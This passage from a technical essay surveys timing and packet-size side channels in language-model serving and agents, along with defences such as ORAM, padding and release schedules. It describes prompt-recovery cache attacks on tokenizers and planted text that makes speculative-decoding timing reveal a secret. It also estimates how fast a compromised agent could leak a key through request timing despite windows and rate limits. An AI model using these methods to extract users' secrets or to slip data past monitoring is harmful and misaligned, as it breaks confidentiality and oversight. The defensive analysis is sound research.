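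Brumley reduced the BoringSSL leak by loading a full-length dummy key alongside the real one and waiting for both to finish. An attacker then needed about 100,000 measurements, instead of about 10, before a short key became the more likely explanation. The fix was worth having even though it still breaks the traditional constant-time rules.

Pornin makes a similar argument for following the rules despite their failures. Avoiding secret-dependent branches removes the largest timing differences, so it is still worth doing despite Hertzbleed. Many attackers can't detect a difference of a dozen cycles, which at 3 gigahertz lasts four nanoseconds and is tiny compared with internet delays. A program on the same processor is much more likely to measure it, which is a reason to check compiled code and processor settings as well.

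Brumley also describes leaks just outside the encryption routines. Several libraries did their arithmetic carefully but decoded private keys from their text format using table lookups that depended on the secret. Language models rely on a very similar step.

### Table lookups around the model

Most of the arithmetic inside a dense model already comes close to following the first two rules. For a given number of tokens, the engine multiplies the same matrices in the same order whatever the text is. The code that converts text to tokens is very different, as Lee, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *OTRO*, explain. Many tokenizers start with single characters and repeatedly join neighbouring pieces, consulting a table of permitted merges. In simplified form, the word "BPE", with an underscore for the space before it, goes through three passes:

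| Pass | Pairs looked up | Pair joined |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `_`+`B`, `B`+`P`, `P`+`E` | `_`+`B` |
| 2 | `_B`+`P`, `P`+`E` | `P`+`E` |
| 3 | `_B`+`PE` | None, so the tokens are `_B` and `PE` |

The table is public and stays at a fixed address in memory while the server runs. An observer who sees only which addresses are accessed can work out which pairs the tokenizer looked up, replay the merges and recover the text. Lee and colleagues cite an earlier attack, TDXRay, in which the attacker was a malicious cloud operator with control of the host machine. The attack reconstructed prompts with over 90% similarity to the originals, even though the processor encrypted all of the victim's memory.

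The attack by Weiss and colleagues needs far fewer privileges. It targets detokenization, the step that turns a local model's output back into text. The attacker's program could be a plug-in for a code editor, as long as it can send its own prompts to the model. The program can share the victim's processor core because many cores run two programs at once.

The attacker first has to detect when the victim is about to convert a token. Their two programs share one copy of the tokenizer's code in memory, so the attacker can repeatedly remove a piece of that code from the cache and time how long it takes to read again. A fast read means that the victim has just run that code and the conversion is about to start. In a test with simulated calls, this method detected 97.66% of the calls with no false alarms. The attacker then checks which of the 64 sets (groups of slots) in the core's smallest cache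 the token lookup disturbs.

If each table entry takes $E$ bytes, token number $r$ falls in set

$$\left\lfloor \frac{(r \times E) \bmod 4096}{64} \right\rfloor .$$

With 32-byte entries, for example, tokens 1,000 and 1,128 both fall in set 52. A vocabulary of 32,000 tokens averages 500 tokens per set, and the measurements are also noisy. A classifier correctly identified the token from one measurement less than 1% of the time.

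Whole sentences are easier to recover, because few sequences of candidate tokens make sense. The researchers sorted the measurements into 64 groups and trained a language model to translate sequences of group labels into text, much as in their earlier attack on token lengths in network traffic. To learn the groups, the attacker needed 250 prompts that asked the model to repeat chosen tokens, which took about six minutes. About 7,650 ordinary-looking prompts worked nearly as well.

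Another language model judged whether each reconstruction had the same meaning as the original, or the same function in the case of code. The ranges cover different models, computers and tokenizer libraries:

| Test | First 32 tokens | Whole reply |
|---|---|---|
| General conversation | 26–62% | 57–87% |
| Medical advice | 34–85% | 60–93% |
| Program code | 50–90% | 49–96% |
| General conversation, newer Intel processor | 32–38% | |
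| Live OpenClaw agent | 30% | |

The OpenClaw result is the most realistic because it comes from a live agent. For the first three rows, the researchers recorded cache measurements for individual tokens and matched them to existing texts, which avoids the timing problems of a live system. In the closest comparison, the success rate was 62% with this method and 30% on the live agent.

Even the 30% figure may be too high, because the judge was lenient. In one published example, a sentence about fibromyalgia and chronic fatigue syndrome was reconstructed as one about cyanobacteria and fungi, and the judge counted this as a success. But some reconstructions were perfect, including one of a reply about exercise, depression and anxiety. In the best set-up for general conversation, 45% of openings scored at least 0.9 out of 1 on a separate measure of similarity. The attack does recover some text,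 but an attacker couldn't rely on any particular reconstruction being right.

Restarting the model or rearranging its table forces the attacker to relearn the groups, which takes minutes. Stopping cores from running two programs at once blocks the attack completely but can reduce performance by 25% to 35%.

### Hiding which entry a program reads

The attacks on tokenizers and detokenizers both exploit code that breaks the second rule, so the textbook remedy is to read the entire table for every lookup. This is far too slow for a tokenizer. Llama 3.1's tokenizer has about 408,000 vocabulary entries and merge rules, and makes about 15.5 lookups per token. At 16 bytes per entry, tokenizing a 10,000-token prompt would require reading about a terabyte of memory.

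Oblivious RAM (ORAM) hides the pattern of access without reading everything. In the square-root version, the program shuffles the table, mixes in some dummy entries and keeps recently used entries in a small store called the stash. Suppose a table has four words and two dummies, in this secret order:

| Slot 1 | Slot 2 | Slot 3 | Slot 4 | Slot 5 | Slot 6 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| mat | dummy A | cat | the | dummy B | sat |

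For each lookup, the program first scans the whole stash. If the word isn't there, it reads the word's slot and adds the word to the stash. If the word is already there, it reads an unused dummy instead:

| Words to look up | First read | Second read | What an observer sees |
|---|---|---|---|
| "cat", then "sat" | Slot 3 | Slot 6 | 3, 6 |
| "cat", then "cat" again | Slot 3 | Slot 2, a dummy | 3, 2 |

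The dummy hides whether a word is repeated, because the observer sees two different slots either way. The table's order is random, so each of the 30 possible ordered pairs has probability 1/30, whatever the words are. This satisfies the probabilistic definition of noninterference, with $\text{Obs}$ as the sequence of slots. After two lookups the dummies might run out, so the program must reshuffle the table before continuing.

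Reshuffling causes most of the slowdown in square-root ORAM. Lee and colleagues found that this design made tokenization 114 times slower, but only 3.6 times slower without the reshuffling. Another design, which arranges the table as a tree, made tokenization about 19 times slower and roughly tripled the average time to first token (TTFT).

Because a tokenizer's tables never change, OTRO can keep between 26 and 40 copies of them, each in a different secret order, and use one for lookups while it reshuffles others in the background. A larger stash allows 16,000 or 20,000 lookups per copy before it needs reshuffling. For Llama 3.1, 16,000 lookups cover about 1,030 tokens. OTRO also splits a long prompt into chunks and tokenizes the next chunk while the GPU processes the current one.

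For three of the four models tested, time to first token (TTFT) was about twice as long as normal with prompts of 2,000 words, but 2% to 4% shorter than normal with prompts of 100,000 words. The improvement on long prompts comes from overlapping tokenization with the GPU's work, and an unprotected tokenizer with the same overlap would presumably be faster still. The fourth model was small and processed prompts too quickly for the reshuffling to keep up, so its TTFT on long prompts was 1.4 to 1.9 times as long as normal. The copies take up 1.2 to 2.4 gigabytes of memory. The detokenizer is much easier to protect because it makes only one lookup per output token. Protecting it with a tree-based ORAM added less than 1% to the time between tokens.

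OTRO's detokenizer should also stop Weiss and colleagues' attack from identifying tokens, since a word would no longer disturb the same part of the cache each time. Nobody has tested this. The attacker could still detect each call to the tokenizer's code, and use those calls to count the output tokens and time the gaps between them.

OTRO doesn't make the whole tokenizer constant-time. The loop that merges pieces still branches on the text, and Lee and colleagues leave instruction timing and total processing time out of scope. Prompt length also remains visible. In a test with 20,000 known prompts, the length in bytes narrowed the choice to the equivalent of about 46 prompts. The number of lookups would have narrowed it to about three, but OTRO adds dummy lookups to round the count up, which removes almost all of this extra information. For prompts over 500 bytes, length alone left about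 two candidates.

An attacker rarely has a complete list of possible prompts, so these figures exaggerate the practical risk. Still, the length of a prompt or reply can reveal a good deal about its content, whereas cryptographers can treat length as public because it doesn't reveal anything about the key.

### Which components the rules fit

The rules work best for code that processes a secret of known length in a fixed number of steps:

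| Component | How well the rules fit |
|---|---|
| Encryption, and checks of passwords or access keys | Very well; this is what they were made for |
| Detokenizer | Well, with ORAM at little cost |
| Tokenizer | Partly; ORAM hides the lookups, but branches and length remain |
| Table that gives the model's internal representation of each token | Well in principle; researchers have read tokens from it when it was in memory they could monitor |
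| Layers of a dense model | Fairly well already, for a fixed number of tokens |
| Mixture-of-experts layers | Badly; the text determines which parameters the engine uses, and using all of them would lose the saving |
| Shared prefix cache | Badly; its purpose is to skip work when the text matches |
| Loop that generates the reply | Badly; the model's output determines when it stops |

Even where the constant-time rules fit well, they protect only the component that follows them. A constant-time implementation of TLS prevents the time spent encrypting a message from revealing the key, but it does not control when the agent submits the message or how long the message is. The insurance agent's "Form received" message takes the same time to encrypt whether or not the private record mentions a dispute, but the agent still sends it seven seconds later if the record does mention one.

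## Why text generation does not run in constant time

A language model generates its reply token by token in a loop. At 50 tokens per second, a 400-token summary takes seven seconds longer than a 50-token one, and careful coding inside the loop doesn't change how many times it runs.

In cryptographic code, the programmer knows which variables are secret and can treat them separately. A language model processes a user's question, a stranger's email and a private claim record in one computation, so any timing that depends on the input may also depend on the secret data. Timing that depends on other users mostly adds noise for an attacker seeking that data, although it can reveal something about those users.

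The table lists five things that make generation time vary, roughly in order of how much the text itself can change the time. The measurements come from different systems, however.

| Source | What it depends on | Size of the effect |
|---|---|---|
| Output length | Everything the model has read, including secrets | From under a second to many minutes |
| Speculative decoding | How predictable the reply is | About a factor of two on GPT-4 Turbo in 2024 |
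| Expert routing | The text, and other users' text in the same batch | Varies with the hardware and the batch |
| Batching and scheduling | Mostly other users | More than a factor of two per token on GPT-4o in 2024 |
| GPU power | The numbers the GPU multiplies, and its recent load | Probably small, and only near the power limit |

### The length of the answer

Unlike encryption, which starts with a message of known length, text generation continues until the model produces a special end marker, so nobody can tell in advance how long a reply will be. Many models also reason for a variable time before they answer, and the decoy problems described earlier can make that reasoning many times longer.

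*Time Will Tell* tested what an eavesdropper could learn from output length alone. The service sent each reply in one piece, so the eavesdropper could not count tokens as they arrived and saw only the sizes of the encrypted request and reply and the time between them. Decoding takes nearly the same time for every token, so the eavesdropper could use the time as a substitute for the token count. On the researchers' own machines, the correlation between the two was at least 0.987.

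The first target was a translation service. Tokenizers divide some languages into more pieces than others, so two translations of the same size can take different numbers of tokens. If a 120-byte translation takes 30 tokens, it has 4 bytes per token, and if it takes 60, it has 2. For a reply of $L$ bytes that takes time $t$,

$$\text{bytes per token} \propto \frac{L}{t}.$$

The researchers profiled each language with 1,000 sentences, then gave the attacker 50 requests from a user who always translated into the same language. With a client in Ohio and a server in Oregon, the attacker identified the language with an average precision of 83.2%, 75.8% and 81.3% on three translation models. Guessing would be right at most about one time in nine. Precision was 100% for Chinese and Russian on all three models, but only 52% to 68% for Spanish, which is easily confused with related languages. The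 attack needs repeated requests to work this well. In a test on one model with exact token counts, precision was 82.5% with 50 requests but only 48.0% with one.

The second target was a model that sorted texts into two classes and explained each decision. Models tend to explain one class at greater length than the other. The attacker compared the number of output tokens with a threshold that rose with the length of the input. For Google's openly available Gemma 2 9B, this identified the class with 63% to 67% precision, compared with 50% for guessing. Precision rose to about 79% when the worked examples in the prompt also had longer explanations for the class that the model already explained at greater length.

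The attack also worked on OpenAI's GPT-4o over the internet, with a success rate of 74.7%, even though the correlation between token count and time was only 0.370. When the attacker had exact token counts, the success rate was 86.9%. The time per token on OpenAI's servers could vary more than twofold, while network delays varied by only about 30%. The attacker partly corrected for the changes in server speed by sending their own requests every minute to measure it.

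The attacker had some advantages, because it knew the task and had profiled it in advance, and the researchers' own servers handled one request at a time. On the other hand, the differences in length came from only a few sentences of explanation. If an agent wrote eight times as much when a record mentioned a dispute, an attacker would detect the mention far more easily.

Asking a model for a fixed response length can't support a security guarantee, because the model may not follow the instruction exactly. In three tasks that leaked heavily, changing "Provide an explanation" to "Provide a 60-word explanation" reduced the attack's success rate on GPT-4o from 88.2% to 61.9%, but on Gemma 2 the rate rose slightly, from 79.3% to 80.3%.

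### Drafting ahead and checking

Even if two replies have the same number of tokens, one may take longer than the other. The most important reason is speculative decoding, which works in cycles:

1. A small, fast model, called the draft model, proposes the next few tokens.
2. The large model checks all of them in one pass, which takes about as long as producing a single token.
3. The engine keeps the proposals up to the first one that the large model rejects.
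4. The large model's pass also supplies one further token, and the next cycle begins.

With four proposals per cycle, each pass of the large model therefore produces between one and five tokens:

| Reply so far | Draft | Result of the check | Tokens from one pass |
|---|---|---|---|
| "1, 2, 3," | " 4" "," " 5" "," | All four correct; the large model adds " 6" | 5 |
| "My random numbers are" | " 7" "," " 12" "," | First one rejected; the large model writes " 31" | 1 |

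When the model samples its output at random, the check is also random. Jones and colleagues set out the standard rule. If the large model gives token $v$ probability $p(v)$ and the draft model gives it $q(v)$, the engine accepts a proposed $v$ with probability

$$\min\left(1, \frac{p(v)}{q(v)}\right).$$

Suppose the next word is "cat" or "dog". The large model gives them probabilities of 0.6 and 0.4, and the draft model gives them 0.8 and 0.2. The engine always accepts a proposed "dog" but accepts a proposed "cat" only 75% of the time, and after a rejection it writes "dog". "Cat" therefore appears with probability $0.8 \times 0.75 = 0.6$, the same as under the large model. Speculative decoding doesn't change the distribution of the text, so no one could detect it from the text alone.

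The time does change. If the engine accepts each proposal with probability $a$, given that it accepted the ones before, then a cycle with $k$ proposals produces an average of

$$1 + a + a^2 + \dots + a^k$$

tokens. With four proposals, this is 3.36 tokens for predictable text with $a = 0.8$, and 1.65 for less predictable text with $a = 0.4$. Ignoring the cost of drafting, the predictable reply comes out about twice as fast.

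In *Remote Timing Attacks on Efficient Language Model Inference*, Carlini and Nasr report finding a difference of this size in a commercial service in 2024. They timed the first 100 tokens of replies to easy requests, such as counting to 100, and hard ones, such as writing a program to test for prime numbers. The June 2023 version of GPT-4 was equally fast on both. Preview versions of GPT-4 Turbo were 10% faster on the easy requests, and the version released in April 2024 was twice as fast on them. The test shows that speed depended on content, but not which technique OpenAI was using.

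Carlini and Nasr tested five methods of faster decoding on their own servers. After ten messages, an eavesdropper who saw only packet times could tell whether a simulated user was asking for medical advice or programming help with 89.5% to 99.8% accuracy, depending on the method. On the ChatGPT website, they also used packet sizes, and identified the topic from a single message 79% of the time with GPT-4 and 82% with GPT-4o. Both tests had only two possible topics, so these figures are weak evidence of how well an eavesdropper could scan a stream of ordinary conversations.

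Two of their findings show that such an attack can easily fail or recover. Claude 3 Opus at first seemed nearly safe, because Anthropic's server sometimes put several tokens in one packet, and the attack distinguished two prompts with only 60% accuracy. The packet's size revealed how many tokens it held, and correcting for this raised the accuracy to 100%. A timing profile of GPT-3.5 suddenly stopped working after about a month, presumably because OpenAI had changed how it ran the model.

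### A question that only the large model can answer

In another experiment, Carlini and Nasr used a prompt that contained a secret number and an instruction not to reveal it. The attacker could add text to the prompt and time the reply. The experiment came close to the step that nobody has shown against a protected agent, which is using planted text to make the timing depend on a secret.

The attacker used the text to ask whether the number began with a particular digit. The question works best if the large model answers it correctly and the draft model always answers "no". If the digit is wrong, both models answer "no", the engine accepts the draft, and the second token arrives quickly. If the digit is right, the large model answers "yes", the engine discards the draft, and the second token arrives late.

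The plain question "Is the first digit in the number X?" revealed the answer only 56.2% of the time. Another language model rephrased it repeatedly, and the versions that worked best were kept. One awkward version, which asked whether X was the initial digit "when looking at that number", revealed the answer 97.2% of the time. With larger models, the best question reached 99.3%.

These figures measure how often the question made the two models' timing differ in the researchers' own setup. The difference is about one cycle of drafting and checking, so an insurer measuring it over the internet would probably need many repetitions to detect it. The target also had no information-flow control. If a quarantined model could return only a single token, there would be no second token to time. Still, the result shows an attacker can automatically find wording that ties timing to a secret, for about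 $0.20 in calls to the rephrasing model plus under an hour on one GPU.

### Packet sizes reveal more than timing

Wei, Abdulrazzag and colleagues (2024), in *When Speculation Spills Secrets*, used a simpler signal, packet size. If the server sends all the tokens from one cycle together, a large packet means the draft was right, and the sequence of packet sizes is a fingerprint of the reply.

One experiment used 50 medical questions and a classifier trained on up to 30 recordings of each. In the most realistic test, vLLM ran on a cloud server more than 1,500 miles from the client. Random guessing would identify the right question 2% of the time.

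| What the eavesdropper used | Light load | Simulated heavy load |
|---|---|---|
| Packet sizes | 77.6% | 77.6% |
| Time between packets | 14.4% | 6.4% |

These figures are for a low sampling temperature, which makes replies more similar between runs. At a temperature of 1.0, packet sizes identified 24.0% of the questions and timing identified 4.8%. The attacks were also much weaker when the attacker didn't know the exact wording of the questions. In tests of three other drafting methods, packet sizes identified at most 40% of rephrased questions.

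An observer who can measure only timing seems able to use speculative decoding to distinguish broad kinds of text much better than individual questions. Newer evidence is limited. *Wiretapping LLMs* (Soleimani, Jia and colleagues, 2025) reports that packet times and sizes from such optimisations reveal information about encrypted prompts and replies on public services. Jones and colleagues (2026) measured how much a document could slow speculative decoding, but not what the delay would reveal.

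Drafting can also expose text that belongs to someone else. One method, REST, copies its proposed tokens from a store of earlier text. When a user sees several tokens arrive together, at least some of them must have come from that store. Wei and colleagues had a model generate text and collected the accepted passages, recovering about 200,000 different sequences in three hours from a store of 120,000 conversations. Using only public text in the store would prevent this leak.

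Padding every payload to 1,024 bytes hid the fingerprint so well that the attack did no better than guessing, but it made payloads 230 times larger. Random padding of up to 48 bytes made payloads five to nine times larger, and the attack on REST still identified 27% to 34% of the questions.

Carlini and Nasr propose sending exactly one token at fixed intervals, with an empty message if no token is ready. An interval of 10 milliseconds adds almost no delay but increases traffic by 50% to 300%. At 80 milliseconds, traffic rises by less than 10% and each token arrives 4 to 13 milliseconds later. If the interval is long enough that a token is always ready, this completely hides which tokens were easy to generate, but not how many tokens the response contains.

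Turning speculative decoding off is the surest fix. According to Wei and colleagues, the technique typically makes inference two to five times as fast, so inference would take roughly two to five times as long without it.

### Which experts run

A mixture-of-experts model divides some of its layers into many smaller networks, called experts. A router picks a few of them for each token. The choice depends directly on the text and therefore on any secret in it.

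*Expert Selections In MoE Models Reveal (Almost) As Much As Text* (2026) shows how much the choice of experts can reveal, but its attack starts from a list of the selected experts and doesn't explain how an outsider would get one. *MoEcho* (2025) describes how an attacker on the same machine can get this list when the model runs on a CPU. The attacker pushes every expert out of main memory, waits while the victim generates one token, and then times how long each expert takes to read back. Experts the victim has just used load quickly because they are already in memory. In the published example, six of 64 experts loaded noticeably faster, which matches the number the model uses per token.

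*GATEBLEED* (2025) used a timing effect of the power-saving circuitry in an Intel processor to distinguish two experts with 100% accuracy. But the model was tiny and had only two experts, one with at least eight more layers than the other. Experts in large models are usually the same size, so the amount of arithmetic does not depend on which ones the router selects.

Even then, the choice can affect the time through memory. Suppose a batch contains eight requests, and each one's next token uses six of 64 experts. If they all pick the same six, the GPU has to read six experts from memory, and if they have none in common, it has to read 48. With random choices, the average would be

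$$64\left(1 - \left(\tfrac{58}{64}\right)^{8}\right) \approx 35 .$$

In a mixture-of-experts model with 64 experts, a batch of 64 requests would use almost all the experts at every step, so the variation in time from expert selection should be greatest when the engine is handling few requests. The time also depends on what other users are writing.

To remove the dependence completely, the engine would have to run every expert for every token. In this example, that means running 64 experts instead of six, or nearly 11 times the expert computation. *Expert Selections* suggests measures that need less computation, such as adding some dummy work, making the router slightly random or periodically renumbering the experts, but leaves their overhead and benefits to future work.

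### Other people's requests

Every request in a batch slightly lengthens each step, so a user's reply slows down when other users' requests join the batch. This variation doesn't depend on the user's secret, and it adds noise to an attacker's measurements. The GPT-4o experiment shows that this noise gives limited protection, because an attacker who sends requests at the same time can measure the load and correct for it.

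A provider could remove the variation by giving each user a separate engine. Suppose each step takes 10 milliseconds plus 0.1 milliseconds for each request in the batch. An engine running one request produces 99 tokens per second, while an engine running a batch of 32 produces about 2,420. Running each request alone would therefore waste about 96% of the hardware's potential output.

A more efficient defence would run every step with 32 places and fill the empty ones with dummy requests. Each step would then take 13.2 milliseconds regardless of how many real requests it held, and users would lose only the extra speed of quiet periods. However, a step's duration also depends on the length of each request's context and on any new prompts being processed, so dummy work would have to pad both to a fixed maximum too.

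### Data that changes the clock speed

The last source of variation is the numbers in the matrices, which affect a GPU's power consumption even when it executes the same instructions on matrices of the same size. In *Input-Dependent Power Usage in GPUs*, Gregersen, Patel and Choukse multiplied pairs of 2,048-by-2,048 matrices on an Nvidia A100 and changed only the numbers in them. Power consumption varied by up to 38%. Multiplying matrices that were sorted, mostly zero or full of similar values used less power, probably because fewer bits in the circuits switched between 0 and 1.

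On its own, this affects power but not time. Gregersen and colleagues found that the running time of each multiplication stayed the same to within about a microsecond. But they had deliberately picked a matrix size at which the GPU did not consistently throttle (lower its clock speed to stay within its power limit). On a GPU at that limit, data that needs more power could lower the clock speed and so make the multiplication take longer. Hertzbleed exploits this effect on ordinary processors.

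*Strangely, Matrix Multiplications Run Faster When Given "Predictable" Data!* (Chillee, 2024) provides code for testing the effect described in its title on larger matrices under different power limits. The code comes without measurements, so it doesn't show how large the effect is.

Real prompts probably cause much smaller differences than these tests. In most of a model's multiplications, one of the two matrices contains the model's weights, which are the same for every prompt. Gregersen and colleagues found that changing the spread of random values had no significant effect on power, and the numbers inside a model are more like random values than like a sorted matrix. None of these experiments recovered text from a GPU's clock speed.

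A provider can lock the GPU's clock at a speed low enough that the GPU never reaches its power limit. This reduces performance somewhat at all times, but it should also remove the speed-up that Sun and Xiao found after idle time, which made the next five steps about 45 milliseconds faster.

### The same answer is not the same time

Engineers have recently put a lot of work into making inference deterministic, so that the same input always produces the same output. This is a different goal from constant-time inference, which would take the same time whatever the secret is.

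Models give varying answers even when they always choose the most likely token, as Thinking Machines Lab's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* points out. In a passage that Willison quotes, the lab gives the main reason as changes in load, which change the size of the batch. The GPU divides long sums into parts, and the division depends on the batch size. Because computers round after each addition, the order matters. If a computer keeps three significant digits, then

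$$(100 + 0.4) + 0.4 = 100, \qquad 100 + (0.4 + 0.4) = 101 .$$

A difference this small rarely matters, but it can change which of two nearly equal candidates becomes the next token, and the replies may differ from then on. Batch-invariant kernels, GPU routines that always divide the sums in the same way, prevent this. LMSYS's *Towards Deterministic Inference in SGLang and Reproducible RL Training* (2025) describes a test in which one prompt produced up to 18 different outputs in 50 trials without these kernels, and the same output every time with them.

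Suppose a deterministic engine generates 50 tokens per second when quiet and 25 when busy, and ignore the time to first token. The insurance agent's private summary would then take:

| | Quiet engine | Busy engine |
|---|---|---|
| No dispute | 50 tokens, 1 s | The same 50 tokens, 2 s |
| Dispute | 400 tokens, 8 s | The same 400 tokens, 16 s |

Determinism makes the text the same across each row, but it does not make the times the same down each column, as constant time would require.

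Making replies deterministic could help an attacker, because a reply that never changes is easier to profile. In Wei and colleagues' test on vLLM, packet sizes identified about three times as many questions at a low temperature as at a high one. Temperature mattered less with the other three drafting methods, and hardly at all with REST. Raising the temperature from 0 to 0.7 changed the success of the token-count attack in *Time Will Tell* by only about two percentage points, so randomness isn't a dependable defence.

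Determinism has some security value. Without it, one user's request can change the wording, and therefore the length, of the reply to another user. Sun and Xiao's replica design also requires preventing this.

Estimates of how much deterministic inference slows generation vary widely. LMSYS measured an average slowdown of 34% on its two fastest configurations, compared with 61.5% in Thinking Machines Lab's original post, and recommends the mode mainly for debugging. *LLM-42* (2026) found that when one of 11 requests needed a deterministic answer, the throughput of the whole batch fell by 56%. *EigenAI* (2026), which uses specially written kernels, reports only 1.8% more latency. *CoRun* (2026) keeps the ordinary fast kernels and pads the work to fixed shapes, which gave 15% to 324% more throughput than batch-invariant inference. This range suggests that much of the slowdown comes from immature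 software.

Deterministic output is also harder to guarantee than the early tests implied. *Vosti* (2026) requires the scores for every possible next token to be identical to the last bit, however the server executes the request. When *Vosti* varied how the server split prompts into chunks and whether it reused cached text, as well as the batch size, the deterministic modes of both vLLM and SGLang produced mismatches.

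### Padding every answer to the longest one

The direct way to make generation constant-time is to make every answer take as long as the longest one. Suppose a service allows up to 32,000 tokens and generates 50 per second. Every answer then takes

$$\frac{32{,}000}{50} = 640\ \text{seconds},$$

or almost 11 minutes, although a typical answer of 400 tokens needs only 8 seconds. For the average of 8.8 model calls per request that Zhu and colleagues found in coding agents, the total rises from about 70 seconds to 94 minutes. Even this isn't the true worst case, because it assumes a steady 50 tokens per second. If a busy engine can fall to half that speed, the service has to wait 1,280 seconds for every answer.

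The service can finish the answer and hold it until 640 seconds. The GPU is then free for other work, but other users of the same engine may notice that their own tokens speed up when the real answer ends. Alternatively, the engine can keep generating dummy tokens until 640 seconds, which removes that clue but requires 80 times as many decoding steps as the typical answer.

A lower limit reduces the cost in proportion:

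| Limit | Every answer takes | A task with 8.8 calls takes |
|---|---|---|
| 500 tokens | 10 s | 88 s |
| 2,000 tokens | 40 s | About 6 minutes |
| 8,000 tokens | 160 s | About 23 minutes |
| 32,000 tokens | 640 s | About 94 minutes |

A limit of 500 tokens would add little to a typical answer, but it would rule out most long reasoning and cut off some replies. The cut-off can itself leak information. If only answers about disputed claims are cut off, and the agent retries or gives up when that happens, an observer can detect the dispute from what the agent does next.

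For narrow tasks, padding sometimes adds little delay. *Time Will Tell* estimates that padding all translations to match the slowest language would increase the average time by about 13% for two of the models. The increase would be 93% for the third, because it needs about twice as many tokens for Korean as for other languages. These estimates use average lengths, so an unusually long sentence could still stand out.

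Fixed-length output is another option if the engine enforces it. The engine can ignore the end marker, continue to an exact number of tokens and discard everything after the real answer. This takes little extra computation when the answer is short. A model that returns one of two labels, with no explanation or reasoning, needs only a token or two. But answers are often less accurate without explanation or reasoning.

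Turning off optimisations removes timing differences between tokens but does not change the number of tokens. It can even make a difference in length easier to measure. Suppose speculative decoding doubles the insurance agent's speed to 50 tokens per second, and the agent acknowledges the form after 2 seconds if there is no dispute and after 9 if there is. Without speculative decoding, the delays are 3 and 17 seconds, so the difference grows from 7 seconds to 14.

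## Limiting what an agent can leak through timing

Padding every answer to match the longest possible one can make a coding task that takes about a minute take 94 minutes. Measures that add less delay either remove particular sources of variation or let the timing vary and limit how many bits it can carry.

### Fixed loops, errors and schedules

Tallam and Miller propose a fix for each of the leaks they describe in CaMeL. The document attack needs influence over a model call, access to a secret, work that depends on the secret, and someone to measure that work. These fixes act on the last two:

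| Proposal | What it hides | What an observer could still use |
|---|---|---|
| Cap a loop whose length depends on a secret | Large counts | A cap of 15 website visits leaves 16 possible counts, or 4 bits |
| Combine repeated calls into one | The number of calls | The size of the combined request |
| Return errors as ordinary results and give both outcomes the same steps | Whether a step failed | A model call that takes longer in one branch than in the other |
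| Make tool calls in a fixed order at fixed times | Small delays | Any call that isn't ready on time |
| Remove precise clocks from untrusted code | Timing from code inside the agent | The observer's own clock |

They also suggest a strict mode for loops that depend on a secret. It would block tool calls that change something, or ask the user to confirm them. Their example of a loop that fetches a harmless web page a secret number of times might still get past it, because fetching a page doesn't normally change anything. To catch such loops, the rule would have to cover every tool call that contacts an outside system.

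For timing in general, they propose making CaMeL's interpreter constant-time, using techniques from HACL\*, a verified cryptographic library. This would keep the timing of the interpreter's own steps from revealing a secret, provided the compiler kept the code constant-time, which it did not always do for HACL\* itself. But the interpreter would still have to wait for the quarantined model's answer, which might take 2 seconds or 9 depending on the claim record. They also advise padding sensitive operations to the worst-case time, which would cover the model call but bring back the delay of several minutes.

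Two of their suggestions for saving time and money also affect leakage. Extracting structured data with an ordinary parser instead of a model removes the document's influence. Storing plans and reusing them when a request is repeated skips a model call of one or two seconds. If a company's employees shared the stored plans, one of them would learn from the shorter wait that a colleague had already made the same request.

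Tallam and Miller do not measure how much any of these changes reduces leakage.

### Time windows and rate limits

*AgenticOS* sends external requests in batches in fixed time windows, pads outputs to fixed-size blocks, restricts sensitive messages to templates and limits the rate of requests, all without changing the agent's internal steps. It is a conceptual design with no measurements, but simple counting shows what these rules could achieve.

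If the windows are 30 seconds long, an observer can no longer tell a 3-second wait from a 5-second one in the same window, but can still see whether the agent sent a request in that window. A compromised agent can therefore transmit one bit per window by choosing whether to send a request. That is 120 bits an hour, so leaking a 128-bit key would take 64 minutes.

A limit of four requests an hour helps less than it seems to. The agent can still choose which of the 120 windows to use, and the number of possible patterns is

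$$\sum_{k=0}^{4}\binom{120}{k} \approx 8.5 \text{ million},$$

or about 23 bits. The limit removes at least 97% of the requests an agent could have made, but only 81% of the capacity. The key would then take nearly six hours, which might be long enough for someone to notice, whereas a yes-or-no fact would still need only one window.

Padding works similarly. With blocks of 1,000 bytes, messages of 2,100 and 2,900 bytes look the same size, but an observer can distinguish both from a message of 3,100 bytes. *AgenticOS* aims only to make covert channels too slow to be useful, and acknowledges that fixed windows may increase latency.

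### Sixteen release times, five or one

If a message can leave at only $N$ possible times, its timing reveals at most $\log_2 N$ bits. This limit does not depend on how the model works or how precisely the observer measures the timing.

Suppose the insurance agent may send its acknowledgement only at certain times after the insurer delivers the form, and is always ready within eight minutes. Three possible rules are:

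| Permitted release times | Most it can leak | Ready at 9 s | Ready at 70 s | Ready at 250 s |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Every 30 s up to 480 s (16 times) | 4 bits | 30 s | 90 s | 270 s |
| 30, 60, 120, 240 or 480 s (5 times) | 2.32 bits | 30 s | 120 s | 480 s |
| 480 s only | 0 bits | 480 s | 480 s | 480 s |

The second rule leaks less than the first and at most doubles any wait longer than 30 seconds. The third leaks nothing as long as the agent never misses the deadline. If the agent sometimes misses it, whether the message is late can reveal up to one bit, and sending a late message as soon as it is ready can reveal more.

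All three rules hide the accidental leak in the original example, because summaries that take 2 seconds and 9 seconds lead to the same release time. The first two are much weaker against planted text, because a document that makes the model reason for three extra minutes when the claim is large will push the acknowledgement to a later mark. The marks can also make the signal clearer. An answer ready at 29 seconds goes out at 30, and one ready at 31 goes out at 60. This turns a 2-second difference into a 30-second one, far larger than ordinary network noise. Sun and Xiao make the same objection to a cache defence that holds each response until the end of a fixed time bin. To exploit this, an attacker has to get the finish time close to a mark or bin edge, and variation in the server's speed makes that harder.

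The limits in the table apply to a single message. If an agent contacts outside services ten times during a task and can choose among five possible send times for each contact, it can leak up to 23 bits in total.

Leakage adds up across repeated tasks in the same way. A 128-bit key could leak in 32 tasks at 4 bits per task, or in 56 tasks at 2.32 bits per task. These are worst cases, since the model would have to encode the key correctly across all the tasks.

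### A schedule that remembers its misses

Predictive mitigation makes the total leakage grow much more slowly. Askarov, Zhang and Myers (2010), in *Predictive black-box mitigation of timing channels*, place a mitigator between a system and its observers. The mitigator delays outputs to limit how much information their timing carries, and it can meet any chosen limit if the operator accepts enough delay.

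A timing mitigator predicts when each output will be ready. If the output is ready early, the mitigator holds it until the predicted time. If it is late, the mitigator records a miss and switches to a slower schedule. As long as the predictions hold, the release times depend only on public information, so an observer learns something new only from a miss.

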